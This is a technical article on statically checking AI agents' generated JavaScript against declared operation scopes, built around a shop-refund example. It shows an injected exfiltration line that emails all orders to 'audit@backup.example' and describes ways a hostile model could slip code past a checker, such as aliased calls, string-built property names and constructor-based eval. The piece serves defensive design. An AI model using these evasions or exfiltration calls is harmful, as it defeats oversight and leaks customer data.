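# Checking model-written JavaScript against a declared set of permitted operations before it runs

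## Checking a program a model has written before it runs

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that lets it act, for example by looking up an order, sending an email or moving money. Many agents now act by writing a short program, usually in JavaScript or Python, that calls the functions for these actions. The whole program exists as text before any of it runs, so other software can read it first and block it. Working out what a program can do by examining its text, without running it, is called static analysis, and compilers and bug-finding tools have used it for decades. A component called the checker uses it to examine each program the model writes, and lets the program run only if it could do nothing outside a fixed set of permissions.

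An operation is an action with an effect outside the program, such as a file write, a network request or a call to an API (the set of functions that one piece of software offers to another). The declared scope is the written statement of which operations a program may perform, with what arguments, how often and on what data.

Checking a program before it runs is attractive because it does not depend on trusting the model. Developers usually gain confidence in a model by testing it, but Meijer points out in *Guardians of the Agents* (2025) that these evaluations, like all software tests, can reveal bad behaviour but cannot prove there is none. A check on the program itself covers the code that is about to run, regardless of how the model behaved in the past.

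### From single calls to whole programs

In direct tool calling, the older arrangement, the model requests one tool at a time. Each request is a small record containing a tool name and some arguments. The host, which is the software around the model, carries out the request and returns the result, and the model then picks the next step. Checking a request is mostly routine. Each tool has a schema that describes the fields a request must contain and their types. The host confirms that the tool's name is on the list and that the arguments fit the schema, and it can show sensitive requests to a person first.

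Companies began having models call tools through programs because that loop is slow and expensive. Cloudflare, an internet infrastructure company, introduced its version, Code Mode, in September 2025, according to *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* (Varda, Pai and Gupta, 2026). Anthropic followed in November with a version in Python. OpenAI released one in JavaScript with GPT-5.6 on 9 July 2026, according to the blog post *Programmatic Tool Calling* (2026). Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* gives the typical example of finding out which members of a twenty-person team overspent their travel budget. With direct calls, the model requests each person's expenses in turn, and more than 2,000 line items pass through its context, the text it has to read. If the model writes a program instead, the program adds up the expenses and the model sees only two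 or three names. On complex research tasks, Anthropic found that this reduced average use by 37%, from 43,588 tokens (the word fragments in which models read and write) to 27,297.

Cloudflare's *Code Mode* documentation describes the model's code as a compact plan that can loop over results, branch on them and pass one call's output to the next. These features make the plan harder to inspect than a direct call, whose arguments are fixed values by the time it reaches the host. In a program, the arguments are expressions, and the call may run once, many times or not at all.

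In *DADL*, a paper on a format for describing APIs to agents, Dunkel (2026) writes that a model's program can still be inspected before it runs, but that inspection becomes "structural code analysis rather than schema matching". His system parses the model's JavaScript, finds the calls on an object named `api`, and checks each one against the caller's role and the tool's access label (read, write, admin or dangerous) before it sends the request. Dunkel presents this as engineering and does not claim a security proof. He lists as an open question how well the system's restrictions on code hold up against deliberately hostile programs.

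Vendors have mostly responded by keeping risky operations out of programs. OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* documentation recommends direct calls by default for writes and for actions that need approval, "to preserve a clear authorization boundary". AI SDK's *Code Mode*, part of a toolkit for building agents, cannot pause a program to ask for approval, so it rejects any call inside a program that needs it. Keeping these operations out is sensible for a host with no checker, but it gives up much of the benefit of using programs. A task with forty refunds goes back to forty requests, and Meijer notes that people who face a stream of consent prompts soon click "Allow" without reading. A checker can allow one meaningful decision about the whole batch.

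The model generates a program from the task and a description of the available functions. The checker reads the text, compares it with the declared scope, and accepts or rejects it. Only accepted text runs, inside an isolated environment. Meijer calls this "generate, verify, then execute". Checking before execution matters most when a program is rejected, because there is nothing to undo and the model can try again. A monitor that watches a running program may stop the tenth call, but the first nine have already had their effects. *CaveAgent* (2026), an agent system that applies rules to the structure of generated code, returns each violation to the model as a structured error so that the model can retry.

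### The shop assistant

Suppose a shop has an assistant, and a member of staff types: refund last week's late orders and email the customers. The assistant may use three functions, `api.listOrders`, `api.refund` and `api.sendEmail`. The object `api` is the host API, the only route the host provides from the program to the outside world. A competent model might write this:

```js
const orders = await api.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" });
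const late = orders.filter(o => o.deliveredOn > o.promisedOn);
for (const order of late) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
  await api.sendEmail({
    to: order.customerEmail,
    subject: "Refund for order " + order.id,
    body: "Your order arrived late, so we have refunded it in full."
  });
}
return late.length;
```

The word `await` pauses the program until the host responds. The second line keeps only the orders whose delivery date is after the promised date, and the loop handles these one at a time.

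A checker does not work on this text as a string of characters. Searching for the letters `api.refund` would flag a comment that mentions refunds, and it would miss a program that first stores the function under another name. The checker starts from a syntax tree, the structured form that a parser makes of the text, in which every expression hangs beneath the statement that contains it. In outline:

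```
Program
├─ declare orders
│   └─ await
│       └─ call  api.listOrders
│           └─ object { from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" }
├─ declare late
│   └─ call  orders.filter
│       └─ function  o => o.deliveredOn > o.promisedOn
├─ for each order of late
│   ├─ await
│   │   └─ call  api.refund
│   │       └─ object { orderId: order.id, amount: order.total }
│   └─ await
│       └─ call  api.sendEmail
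│           └─ object { to: order.customerEmail, subject: ..., body: ... }
└─ return late.length
```

The tree shows that the program calls only three functions of the host API. The program lists orders once, for a date range that appears in full, and makes the refund and email calls inside a loop. The tree doesn't show how many orders were late, what each one cost, or whose address `customerEmail` will hold, because those values don't exist until the program runs.

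*Agents as Software* (Barke and Murali, 2026) uses almost the same case to set out three things an analysis should check before execution. The paper considers an agent's whole configuration, including its prompts and tool descriptions, but the checks also suit a single program. The first is whether each call is valid by itself, with an amount above zero and no larger than the order's total. The second is whether the call's arguments come from a legitimate source, such as an order number returned by an earlier lookup rather than invented by the model. The third is whether the program can reach the refund before it has established that the customer is entitled to one. In the shop's program, the order number clearly comes from `listOrders`, and a single comparison in the second line determines whether the customer is entitled to the refund.

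### Why a program might leave its scope

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) attributes agents' misuse of tools to misalignment, prompt injection, hallucination and simple error. A checker can treat hallucination and error alike as mistakes, which leaves three cases with different requirements for the checker.

A model can make a mistake, such as writing `>=` where it needed `>`, so that the shop refunds every order that arrived on the promised day. It can also take a shortcut. Meijer describes a request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt` that a model might satisfy by deleting every text file, because that program is shorter. Such errors are common enough to plan for. The survey *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) cites a benchmark of 105 secure-coding tasks in C and C++ on which the best pairing of coding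 agent and model produced correct and secure solutions 23.8% of the time. Those tasks are much harder than writing a ten-line script, so we can infer little from the figure about how often the shop's assistant would make such errors.

A mistaken program looks like ordinary code, with nothing concealed, so a checker that handles ordinary code will detect what it does. But the declared scope has to be specific enough to exclude the mistake. If the scope permits `api.refund` without saying for which orders, the program with `>=` stays within it and any checker will pass it.

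Prompt injection is text, in data the model reads, that makes it follow an attacker's instructions. Meijer's example is an email that tells an assistant to back up the mailbox to an outside address and not to mention it. In the shop, the equivalent might be one extra line:

```js
await api.sendEmail({ to: "audit@backup.example", subject: "Backup", body: JSON.stringify(orders) });
```

This line uses a permitted function correctly, so a check against a list of allowed names would pass it. Dunkel makes the general point that injected text can now introduce code that combines calls in unexpected ways, even though each call still gets its own permission check. The checker therefore has to examine the arguments and which data can flow into them.

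If the model finishes the program before it reads any orders, a note hidden in an order cannot add a line to the code. Hostile text may still have reached the model earlier, in a tool's description, a previous tool result or something the user pasted. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) cites a finding from CaMeL, a Google DeepMind defence that keeps untrusted text away from the model that plans, that isolation alone may not stop an attacker from changing the values passed to a correctly chosen call. For example, an attacker who can edit the `customerEmail` field receives the shop's email even though the program is correct.

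The third case is a model that works against the restriction. The threat model of Odersky and colleagues assumes that the cloud-hosted model may be "byzantine", meaning that it may fail in any way, up to full cooperation with an attacker. Such a model may use knowledge of the checker's rules to produce code they miss, such as a function under a new name, a property name assembled from pieces, or code built while the program runs. CaveAgent's rules block unauthorised imports, dangerous calls such as `eval()` and attributes that help code escape its sandbox, but rules of this kind catch only what their writers thought of. Against a hostile model, the checker must accept only constructs it can fully account for and reject everything else, including code that merely looks odd.

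A program's text doesn't reveal which of the three causes produced it. The last two overlap anyway, since a skilled attacker can inject instructions to write evasive code. It seems safest to build the checker to withstand a hostile author and to write the scope with a careless one in mind.

### Soundness, and what it costs

The checker is sound if every program it accepts stays within the declared scope on every possible run, whatever the host API returns. A false rejection occurs when the checker refuses a program that would always stay within the scope. Soundness always depends on stated assumptions. Odersky and colleagues, for instance, trust their compiler, their library and the runtime that executes the code, and a bug in any of these would void the guarantee.

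Soundness alone is easy to achieve, since a checker that rejects every program is sound. A theorem that Henry Rice published in 1953 rules out a sound checker that also has no false rejections, for which *A* would equal *S*. Rice's theorem concerns properties of what programs do, not how their text looks. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no procedure can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has the property. *Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) applies the theorem to whether an agent "only accesses approved APIs" or "stays within its refund limit", both properties a shop would care about.

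The reasoning fits in two lines of code.

```js
puzzle();   // makes no api call and throws no error, but may run forever
await api.refund({ orderId: "A-1001", amount: 1000000 });
```

If the scope forbids that refund, the program leaves its scope exactly when `puzzle` finishes. A checker that always gave a correct answer would therefore show whether `puzzle` finishes, and would do the same for any computation put in its place. Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no procedure can tell, for every computation, whether it finishes. If such a procedure existed, one could write a program that applies it to the program's own text, then stops if the verdict is "runs forever" and runs forever if the verdict is "stops", so either verdict would be wrong.

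In *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, Pérez-Acle (2026) uses the same device, a program that solves a puzzle and then opens a safe, in his proof about gatekeepers for AI-written code. One version opens the safe only if it finds an even number that is not the sum of two primes. That program is safe if and only if Goldbach's conjecture, which he lists as an open problem, is true. He also shows that adding rules never makes a rulebook complete, because any sound rulebook of *n* bits fails to certify some compliant program of about *n* bits.

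Pérez-Acle proves that limiting how long a program can run helps a checker very little. Hosts do cut programs off, often after about thirty seconds, and a fixed limit makes every question of this kind answerable, but an always-correct checker must take essentially the whole time limit on some programs. The shop's case is harder still, because a trial run would need the list of late orders, which doesn't exist until `api.listOrders` returns it.

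So a sound checker that always reaches a verdict will reject some harmless programs. How much this matters depends on which programs it rejects. If `puzzle` never finishes, the two-line program above is harmless because it never reaches the million refund, and the shop loses nothing by refusing it because no one needs a program that hangs. Pérez-Acle's simulations on 2.2 million random programs and on purpose-built ones also suggest that the obstruction is "adversarial rather than typical". His positive result is more useful to someone building a gatekeeper. The gatekeeper needs a checkable set that includes every program it must admit and none that it must refuse. It can admit or refuse any other program, so it doesn't have to classify every program correctly.

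Rice's theorem also doesn't apply to questions about a program's text. For example, a checker can walk the syntax tree once to determine whether every appearance of `api` is part of a direct call to one of three named functions. If the program passes and the language offers no other way to reach anything outside the program, it can perform only those three operations. The check also rejects some programs that stay within the permitted operations, such as one that stores `api.refund` under a shorter name and uses it properly.

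Current systems make this trade openly. *Soteria* (2026), which verifies model-written plans before execution, rejects any plan that *may* violate a policy. CaMeLoT turns a plan in restricted Python into a finite map of its possible steps, and assumes that a loop can either repeat or exit at each pass. The map therefore contains every real execution and some that could never happen. Nikolaou and colleagues accept that this may block safe plans so that the check doesn't miss any potential violation that runs through a loop. Suppose the shop's scope allowed at most fifty refunds. A checker that modelled loops this way would reject the program above, even in a week with six late orders, because nothing in the code stops the loop at fifty.

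Such a rejection is a nuisance, but the model can rewrite ten lines in seconds, and adding a limit to the loop would satisfy the checker. The main practical concern is how much useful work is still lost after rewriting. Meijer wrote in 2025 that nobody had formally measured how planning in this structured form affects an agent's performance. Odersky and colleagues have since tested a strict version, in which agents write in a restricted form of Scala and the compiler rejects code that uses permissions it does not have. They found no significant loss in task performance. Scala is a typed language with a compiler suited to this kind of checking, so the result does not transfer directly to JavaScript, but it suggests that models can learn to write code that passes a strict checker.

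McCann's answer to Rice's theorem is to judge a program's requests instead of the program itself. In his design, a program can only produce requests, each a finite piece of data, and the host decides on each one as it comes up. These decisions always terminate because the host only has to check a finite record against a rule. The weakness is that the host may deny a request after it has already granted others. If it denies the thirty-first refund, thirty customers already have their money and the program stops halfway through. Run-time decisions are necessary for values that nobody can know earlier, but they are a poor substitute for refusing a bad program before it starts.

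### The precedent of bytecode verification

Java and .NET have used this kind of check for decades. Their programs are usually distributed as bytecode, instructions for a virtual machine, and may come from an untrusted source. The virtual machine therefore verifies the bytecode before running it. Meijer, who proposes extending the idea to agents' plans, says this verification secures memory safety, type correctness and proper access control.

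Bytecode verification is also subject to Rice's theorem, so it tracks the types of values and ignores the values themselves. It must therefore assume that either branch of a test may run, and it rejects code with an ill-typed instruction even in a branch that would never run. Hardly anyone notices, because compilers produce bytecode in forms the verifier accepts, and almost nobody writes the harmless programs it would reject. A model given the checker's rules could likewise write programs in forms the checker accepts.

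The parallel with Java has limits. Java's designers planned for verification, while JavaScript lets a program reach the same function in many ways, so a checker can handle only part of the language. Memory safety also means the same thing for every Java program, but a refund limit applies to one shop, and perhaps to only one task, and somebody has to specify it correctly.

The precedent also shows that some checks have to wait until the program runs. As Meijer notes, verification does not establish that an array index falls within the array, because the index may depend on data that arrives later. The virtual machine instead tests each index when it is used. The value of `order.total` in the shop's program can't be checked in advance either. The checker can establish before the run that the program refunds only through `api.refund` and takes the amount from the order record, and the host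 compares the actual sum with the limit when the call arrives.

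## Stating the permitted operations

A request such as "Refund last week's late orders and email the customers" leaves out most of what a checker needs. It doesn't limit the size or number of refunds, or rule out sending a copy of every email to somebody else. A human assistant would fill these gaps with common sense, but a checker needs a rule for each one that gives a yes or no answer.

### From an instruction to rules

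The usual starting point is default denial, which means refusing any operation that no rule allows. Docker's *MCP policy reference* describes such a system for tools that agents reach through a common standard, the Model Context Protocol. Docker's gateway blocks a tool call unless a `permit` rule matches it, and a matching `forbid` rule overrides any `permit` rule. Default denial keeps a new host function blocked until somebody permits it, whereas a list of forbidden operations would go out of date whenever the host gained a function.

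The rules then have to name the permitted operations. In *pmcp-code-mode*, a library that validates model-written code before running it, the developer lists each operation with a name and a category (read, write, delete or admin). Rules about categories are convenient but can miss operations, because the library also assigns a single category to each whole script. A script that only deletes things counts as a delete, but one that looks something up and then deletes it counts as a write. A rule against delete scripts would miss the second script, while a rule that forbids the delete operation by name would catch it.

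Permitting an operation by name alone usually grants too much access. *AC4A* (Sharma and Grossman, 2026) gives the example of a user who wants an agent to create one calendar event but has to grant access to the whole calendar API, so the agent can also read and change every existing event. The remedy is to limit the arguments as well. For example, one of Docker's sample rules permits `approve_expense` only when the amount is at most 500.

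Such limits belong in permits rather than forbids, because a request may arrive with no amount at all. A permit that requires an amount of at most 500 doesn't match that request, so the gateway blocks it. A forbid on amounts above 500 doesn't match the request either, so the forbid doesn't block it. Docker's sample also has no lower bound, so it would accept an amount of -500.

Two further kinds of rule limit how often a program may call an operation and where data may go. *ToolFence* (2026) combines them in a contract for each permitted call, which sets a call budget and ties each sensitive argument to an approved value. For example, the contract for `send_money(recipient, amount)` permits a single call with the exact recipient and amount approved.

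### The shop's scope in full

Suppose the shop's owner is happy for the assistant to look up orders freely, to refund up to 50 per order at most ten times, and to email only the customers it has refunded. The declared scope might read:

```
Refuse everything except:

listOrders   any arguments, any number of calls

refund       amount:  more than 0 and at most 50
             calls:   at most 10 in the whole task,
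                      and at most 1 for each order

sendEmail    to:      the customerEmail of an order that
                      this task has already refunded
             subject, body:  any text
```

Some of this wording closes loopholes. With only a limit of 50 per call, a program could refund the same order five times, so the scope allows one refund per order. The amount must be above zero because some payment systems might treat a negative refund as a charge.

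The limit of ten covers the whole task because the model may write more than one program. If the first program makes six refunds and then fails on a network error, a fresh limit would let the second make ten more. Zhou and Zhang (2026) describe the same problem in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, where an agent allowed to buy one item delegates the purchase to two others, each with its own allowance of one. They also point out that a request that timed out may have succeeded. The host should keep the count, include any refund that may have succeeded, and give the checker the number remaining.

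The assistant's program from the previous section doesn't meet this scope. `order.total` may be more than 50, and nothing stops the loop at ten.

The scope also permits some unwanted behavior. A program could email one customer the complete list of orders, with everyone's address, because the email body may contain any text. A shop could prevent this by restricting the body to fixed text and details of the recipient's own order. The scope doesn't require a refunded order to be late either, so the `>=` mistake could still pass.

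The shop could write part of this scope in Cedar, an open-source policy language from Amazon Web Services. Using Docker's names, the limit on the amount becomes:

```
permit (principal, action == MCP::Action::"invokeTool", resource)
when {
  resource.name == "refund" &&
  context has args && context.args has amount &&
  context.args.amount > 0 && context.args.amount <= 50
};
```

One reason to use Cedar is that software can analyse its policies. *AutoCedar* (Vatsa, Shome and colleagues, 2026) uses a Cedar tool that translates two policies into logical formulas and decides whether one allows a request that the other denies. If it does, the tool produces an example of such a request.

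But Cedar evaluates each request separately. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) describes it as "stateless by design". Cedar therefore can't count refunds or track which orders the task has refunded. The host has to keep those records and supply them with each request.

Translating a scope from one form to another can also lose part of it. In an example from Zhou and Zhang, a user allows an agent to send one summary to Alice, and the written policy records this correctly. The system then issues the agent a credential that simply permits sending mail. The mail service checks this credential correctly but would still deliver the summary to Bob. To avoid this, Zhou and Zhang require that every effect the implementation allows, described in the policy's terms, is one the policy allows. A checker that reduced the shop's scope to three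 permitted names would not meet this requirement.

### Which rules a checker can decide

The table sorts the shop's rules, and a few it might want to add, by when it is possible to tell whether a program follows them. The safe subset is the part of JavaScript the model may use, chosen so that the checker can analyze it.

| Kind of rule | Examples from the shop | What settles it |
|---|---|---|
| Decidable from the text, in a safe subset | The program calls only the three listed operations. A constant amount such as 20 is in range. A loop over at most ten orders makes at most ten refunds. | The checker, before the run |
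| Decidable for some programs only | `order.total` is never above 50 when the program refunds it. `to` always holds the address of a refunded order. | The checker, if it can prove the point. Otherwise it rejects the program or leaves a test to the host. |
| Dependent on run-time facts | The order exists. Nobody has refunded it already. The shop's balance covers the refund. | The host, at the moment of the call |
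| Beyond any policy check | The program's idea of "late" is the one the user had in mind. | A person |

The theory of enforceable policies explains most of these boundaries. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider studied monitors, which watch a program run and stop it before it takes a forbidden step. A monitor has access only to the current run so far. It can therefore enforce a policy only if the policy judges each run separately and every violation becomes irreversible after a finite number of steps. Such policies are called safety properties. "No refund above 50" and "no eleventh refund" are safety properties. "Every late customer eventually gets a refund" isn't, because the program could always issue any missing refunds later.

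A program that does nothing satisfies every rule in the shop's scope, because the scope only limits what a program may do. The user still has to check whether the program did the job.

Schneider also shows that rules about information flow are not safety properties, because they depend on more than one run. Suppose a program emails a refunded customer "Thank you for your order". The email reveals nothing about the order if every refunded customer gets it, but if it is sent only when the order contained medicine, anyone who sees it learns something private. A monitor watching one run sees the same email in both cases. In practice, monitors enforce a stricter rule, such as Schneider's example, which forbids all sending once the program has read a file. A rule that forbids sending after `listOrders` would be useless to the shop, since every email it sends comes after that call.

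A checker reads the program's text, which describes all its possible runs, so it can compare both branches of a conditional. But it must reach a verdict before the program starts. In *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006), Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider show that the policies a static check can enforce exactly are those for which some algorithm can correctly decide whether any given program complies.

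An algorithm can decide whether a program always finishes within 100 steps, because the program can read at most 100 symbols of input in that time and the algorithm can try every possible input of that length. No algorithm can decide for every program whether it ever performs a forbidden operation, as the `puzzle` example showed, so a static check has to enforce a stricter rule instead. This is why the second row of the table is marked "some programs only". A safe subset makes more of these questions decidable by excluding the programs that are hardest to analyse.

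The third row has a simpler explanation. Hamlen and colleagues model a program as reading its input from a tape whose contents the enforcement mechanism can't read in advance. In this case, the tape holds the shop's order records and bank balance.

A monitor can enforce "never performs a forbidden operation" exactly, by intervening only when the program is about to perform one. Hamlen and colleagues prove that a monitor with access to the program's text can enforce everything a static check can, since it can run the same analysis when the program starts. They note, however, that discovering a violation late may require undoing earlier steps.

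*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) extends the theory to agents whose actions are irreversible. One example is the rule that every payment must eventually be followed by a confirmation. A gate that judges each action as it comes up can't enforce this rule without also blocking compliant runs. If it allows the payment and no confirmation follows, it can't reverse the payment, and if it blocks the payment, it may stop a run that would have included the confirmation.

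The shop's version would be that every refund gets an email. A checker has an advantage here because it can detect that the call to `sendEmail` comes directly after `refund` in the loop. It can then establish that the program will attempt the email after every successful refund, unless the host stops the program in between.

Ray also separates rules that a machine can test exactly, such as a spending cap, from rules that depend on meaning. A judge has to decide whether an email contains personal information. It may be wrong, and a stricter judge will block more harmless emails. The meaning of "late" is even harder to check, because the program doesn't show what the member of staff meant by it. The shop's program keeps an order if `deliveredOn` is after `promisedOn`. A parcel that never arrived has no delivery date, so in JavaScript the comparison is false and the customer gets nothing, which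 the member of staff may not have intended. The shop could add a definition of "late" to the scope, which would also catch the `>=` mistake, but somebody would have to get the definition right.

### Flow rules and files that should stay put

Meijer gives two examples of how to write rules that a program can be proved to satisfy. One forbids data from flowing from the result of `fetch_email` (the source) to the `body` of `send_email` (the destination) when the recipient is outside the company. An analysis tool such as CodeQL or Semgrep can search for a path from the source to the destination, and if it finds one, the host doesn't run the program. (A later section describes how such searches work.) The rule would catch the injected mailbox backup described earlier.

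If the program computes the recipient's address, the checker has to treat it as external unless it can prove otherwise. Meijer's sketch identifies the company's addresses with the pattern `*.valleysharks.com`. As an ordinary wildcard, this pattern requires a dot before the company's name, so `anna@valleysharks.com` doesn't match and the rule would block internal mail. Removing the dot gives `*valleysharks.com`, which would accept `eve@notvalleysharks.com`. Comparing the whole domain is safer.

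The shop can write its missing rule about email bodies in the same form. The source is the result of `listOrders`, and the destination is the `body` of `sendEmail`. The rule forbids text from flowing between them unless the recipient's address comes from the same order as the text.

Meijer's other example, the request to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, shows how a correct proof can approve a bad program. The model's shortcut is to call `delete_file("*.txt")`. Suppose the specification consists of postconditions, which are statements that must be true once the code has finished:

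```
delete_file(pattern)   afterwards, no file matches the pattern
the task               afterwards, foo.txt and bar.txt are gone
```

The program passes because it deletes every text file, including the two named ones. The postcondition specifies what the user wanted to change but not what they wanted to keep. John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described this difficulty in 1969 and named it the frame problem.

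Meijer's solution is a frame condition, which states what must stay the same. He adds one to `delete_file`, saying that files outside the pattern remain as they were, and reports that the `*.txt` program then fails. Strictly, the task needs a frame condition too:

```
delete_file(pattern)   afterwards, no file matches the pattern,
                       and every other file is as it was
the task               afterwards, foo.txt and bar.txt are gone,
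                       and every other file is as it was
```

The condition on the task rules out a program that deletes `*.txt`, because it would also delete files such as `notes.txt`. The condition on the function allows a correct program to pass. Without it, the verifier couldn't establish that deleting `foo.txt` damages nothing else.

Default denial, set by the line "refuse everything except" in the shop's scope, similarly protects all the things nobody thought to mention. But it refuses only operations and arguments that the scope doesn't allow. If the scope allowed `delete_file` with any pattern, it would allow `*.txt`.

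### Who writes the scope

The research is less settled on this question. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) points out that an agent's task often has no developer to set its policy, only a user who types a request and may know nothing about security.

The developer, if there is one, knows the functions but not the task. Developers can set limits that hold for every task, such as a maximum of 50 per refund, and can describe what each function does. Those descriptions may be wrong or go out of date. Zhou and Zhang describe a tool that starts forwarding data to an outside service while its name and arguments stay the same. Docker treats a tool's own description as advisory and assumes the tool is destructive unless it is declared non-destructive.

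The user knows the task but is unlikely to write rules for it. More realistically, the user approves a short list in plain language and decides when the agent may go beyond it. Zhou and Zhang distinguish choosing within a permission from changing the permission. If the user has allowed a message to Alice, the agent may look up her address in a company directory, but it may not copy Bob because a document says to. Similarly, in the shop, the agent can take the customer's address from an order record but can't add a recipient because of a note in that record.

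A model can write a scope for each task in seconds, but this is risky when the same model also writes the program. If an injected claim has misled it into treating a copy to `audit@backup.example` as necessary for every refund, it may permit that address in the scope and then use it in the program. The checker would find that the two agree. ToolFence reduces this risk by having a separate model call write the scope. That call sees only the user's authenticated request and the tool descriptions, with no untrusted content. However, *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) warns that requests can be ambiguous, and that a manipulated prompt may ask for a broader permission than the user intended.

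Models also make ordinary mistakes when they write policies. Vatsa and colleagues gave a model 200 written requirements and compared its Cedar policies with reference policies. When the model wrote the policy directly, it allowed exactly the same requests as the reference in 132 cases (66%). With AutoCedar, it did so in 178 (89%). AutoCedar breaks the requirements into small statements for a person or another model to approve. From the approved statements, it calculates which requests the policy must allow and which it must deny, and a verifier checks the finished policy against these results.

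Of AutoCedar's remaining errors, three were runs that produced no policy. The other 19 were policies that passed every check against their own targets, but the targets were wrong. In 17 of the 19, the targets required the policy to allow requests that the reference denied. Vatsa and colleagues say that they certify a policy against the approved plan, not against what people intended.

One of their examples shows how easily a reviewer could miss such an error. A musician wants to let her band download her new album. A rule that checks whether the user has the role "band member" would also let in the members of every other band, even though it looks right. AutoCedar's check is also weak on rate limits, such as the shop's ten refunds. It confirms only that the rule names a counter and a threshold, so the reviewer has to check the rest.

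A model can also write rules that are too strict. Mondl and colleagues used one to turn 88 written rules for a medical-records agent into Cedar policies, along with some rules taken from existing code. They then replayed recorded runs against these policies, which blocked 94% to 100% of the runs that tried to write to a record on ordinary, non-hostile tasks. Two of the rules that fired most often required the agent to restate the patient's details and get confirmation before writing. The agents may have skipped these steps, but the experiment doesn't show that the policies were usable, because it measured how much of the written policy the rules covered, not how much work an agent could still do under them. Mondl and colleagues warn that developers tend to switch the protection off when policies are too narrow.

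The best arrangement is probably for the developer to set outer limits for all tasks, a model to propose a narrower scope for the task at hand, and the user to approve it. For the parts written in Cedar, the comparison tool can confirm that the proposal allows nothing outside the developer's limits. The model may still misread the request, but its mistakes can't let the program exceed those limits.

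### Testing and proving a machine-written policy

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) checks a model-written policy with both tests and proof. A model turns a safety request in ordinary language into a Python function that takes the details of a proposed action and returns "allow" or "deny". The model also writes constraints that the function must satisfy. For the shop, the function might take the amount of the proposed refund and the number of refunds so far. The constraint would be that it returns "allow" only if the amount is above 0 and at most 50, and there have been fewer than ten refunds so far.

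VeriGuard then refines the policy in three stages. First, a model looks for ambiguities in the request and asks the user about them. If no user is available, the system picks the most plausible answers itself, so a model is again setting its own scope. Next, a model generates test cases, including boundary values and invalid inputs, and revises the function until it passes them or the attempts run out.

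The last stage uses Nagini, a program verifier for Python. Nagini tries to prove a statement of the form {*P*} *f* {*Q*}, meaning that if condition *P* is true before the function *f* runs, condition *Q* will be true afterwards. A proof covers every amount the shop's function could receive, whereas tests might cover only a few, such as 0, 50 and 51. If the proof fails, the model uses the verifier's error or counterexample to revise the function or the constraints. When the agent runs, the finished function checks each action before it takes effect.

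Miculicich and colleagues tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, a collection of attacks on agents. With Google's Gemini 2.5 Flash as the model, attacks succeeded 51.9% of the time on average without a defence, and never with VeriGuard. A simpler defence, which asked a model whether each action complied with the policy, also stopped every attack, but agents completed only 40.2% of their tasks under it, compared with 63.3% under VeriGuard.

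These results are weak evidence about the value of the proof. When Miculicich and colleagues added the stages one at a time, the generated policy alone cut the attack rate from 53.5% to about 10%, and the rate had reached zero before they added formal verification. A proof is most useful for inputs that no test or benchmark includes, so this experiment could hardly have shown its benefit.

The proof also has two weak points. The first is that a model writes the constraints, and Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the guarantee depends on the user confirming that the constraints express what they wanted. The second is at run time, when another model call extracts the facts that the function needs from the agent's text, such as the recipient of an email. If it extracts the wrong recipient, the function's verdict is correct for that recipient but may be wrong for the actual email. A checker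 for JavaScript programs doesn't need this step, because it can read constant arguments from the syntax tree, and the host receives the actual value of every other argument when the program makes the call.

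## Restricting the JavaScript the model may write

The shop's scope is useful only if the checker can find every refund in a program and read its arguments. The assistant's program makes this easy by writing `api.refund` in full at the point of the call, but JavaScript doesn't require that. Each of these lines issues the same refund:

```js
await api.refund(r);
const give = api.refund; await give(r);
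const { refund: pay } = api; await pay(r);
await api["ref" + "und"](r);
```

A checker that looks only for `api.refund(...)` would miss the last three lines. Allowing `api` only in direct calls, as mentioned earlier, is simpler than using the analyses in later sections to follow a function from one name to another, and it doesn't limit what the model's code can do.

### What makes the full language hard to check

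JavaScript also runs functions that a program never visibly calls, which is a worse problem than extra names. When a program joins an object to a string with `+`, JavaScript may call the object's `toString` method, which the program may have defined itself. Reading `order.total` can also run code if `total` is a getter, a property whose value comes from a function that runs each time the property is read.

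Ordinary objects can also lead to powerful ones. *ADsafety: Type-Based Verification of JavaScript Sandboxing* (Politz, Eliopoulos and colleagues, 2015) gives an example from the browser. A program with a direct reference to any element of a web page can reach the page's window in two steps, and the window gives it access to the network, stored data and the user's location. Outside the browser, every string and array inherits properties from JavaScript's built-in objects, and one of these leads to the constructor that turns text into new functions. A program can therefore run a string as code, as `eval` does, without containing the word `eval`.

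A safe subset leaves such features out. People who designed subsets for the web had to persuade developers to give up habits and rewrite old code, but a model writes a new program for each task.

### Permitted lists and forbidden lists

A checker can define its subset by listing what it rejects or by listing what it accepts. In both cases it walks the syntax tree and looks at the kind of each node:

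```
forbidden list    if the kind is on the list, reject the program
                  otherwise, carry on

permitted list    if the kind is on the list, apply the rule for that kind
                  otherwise, reject the program
```

A permitted list applies default denial to syntax, so it rejects any new syntax until somebody has considered it. JavaScript gains new syntax almost every year. In 2020, for example, it gained optional chaining, which lets a program write `api?.refund(r)`. This does the same as `api.refund(r)` as long as `api` exists, but some parsers represent it with a different kind of node. With those parsers, a forbidden list written before 2020 would let the new form through once the parser supported it.

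Omissions are also easier to find in a permitted list than in a forbidden one. If a permitted list lacks a harmless construct, the checker soon rejects a useful program and somebody complains, whereas a dangerous construct missing from a forbidden list has no effect until a program uses it, perhaps on an attacker's behalf.

For each kind of syntax-tree node it permits, the checker has to specify the values that every field may take. For example, JavaScript's recent `using` declaration creates a variable much as `const` does, but it also causes a clean-up method to be called on the variable's value when the block ends. Parsers that follow ESTree, the most common format for JavaScript syntax trees, give both declarations the same kind of node and record the keyword in a field. A checker that permits variable declarations without looking at that field would let in a hidden function call.

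Names need to be restricted in the same way. The shop can let a program use only `api` and a few harmless built-ins without declaring them. It can also limit property names to the fields that `listOrders` returns and some array methods, such as `filter` and `slice`. This excludes `constructor` without a separate rule to ban it.

### A present-day validator

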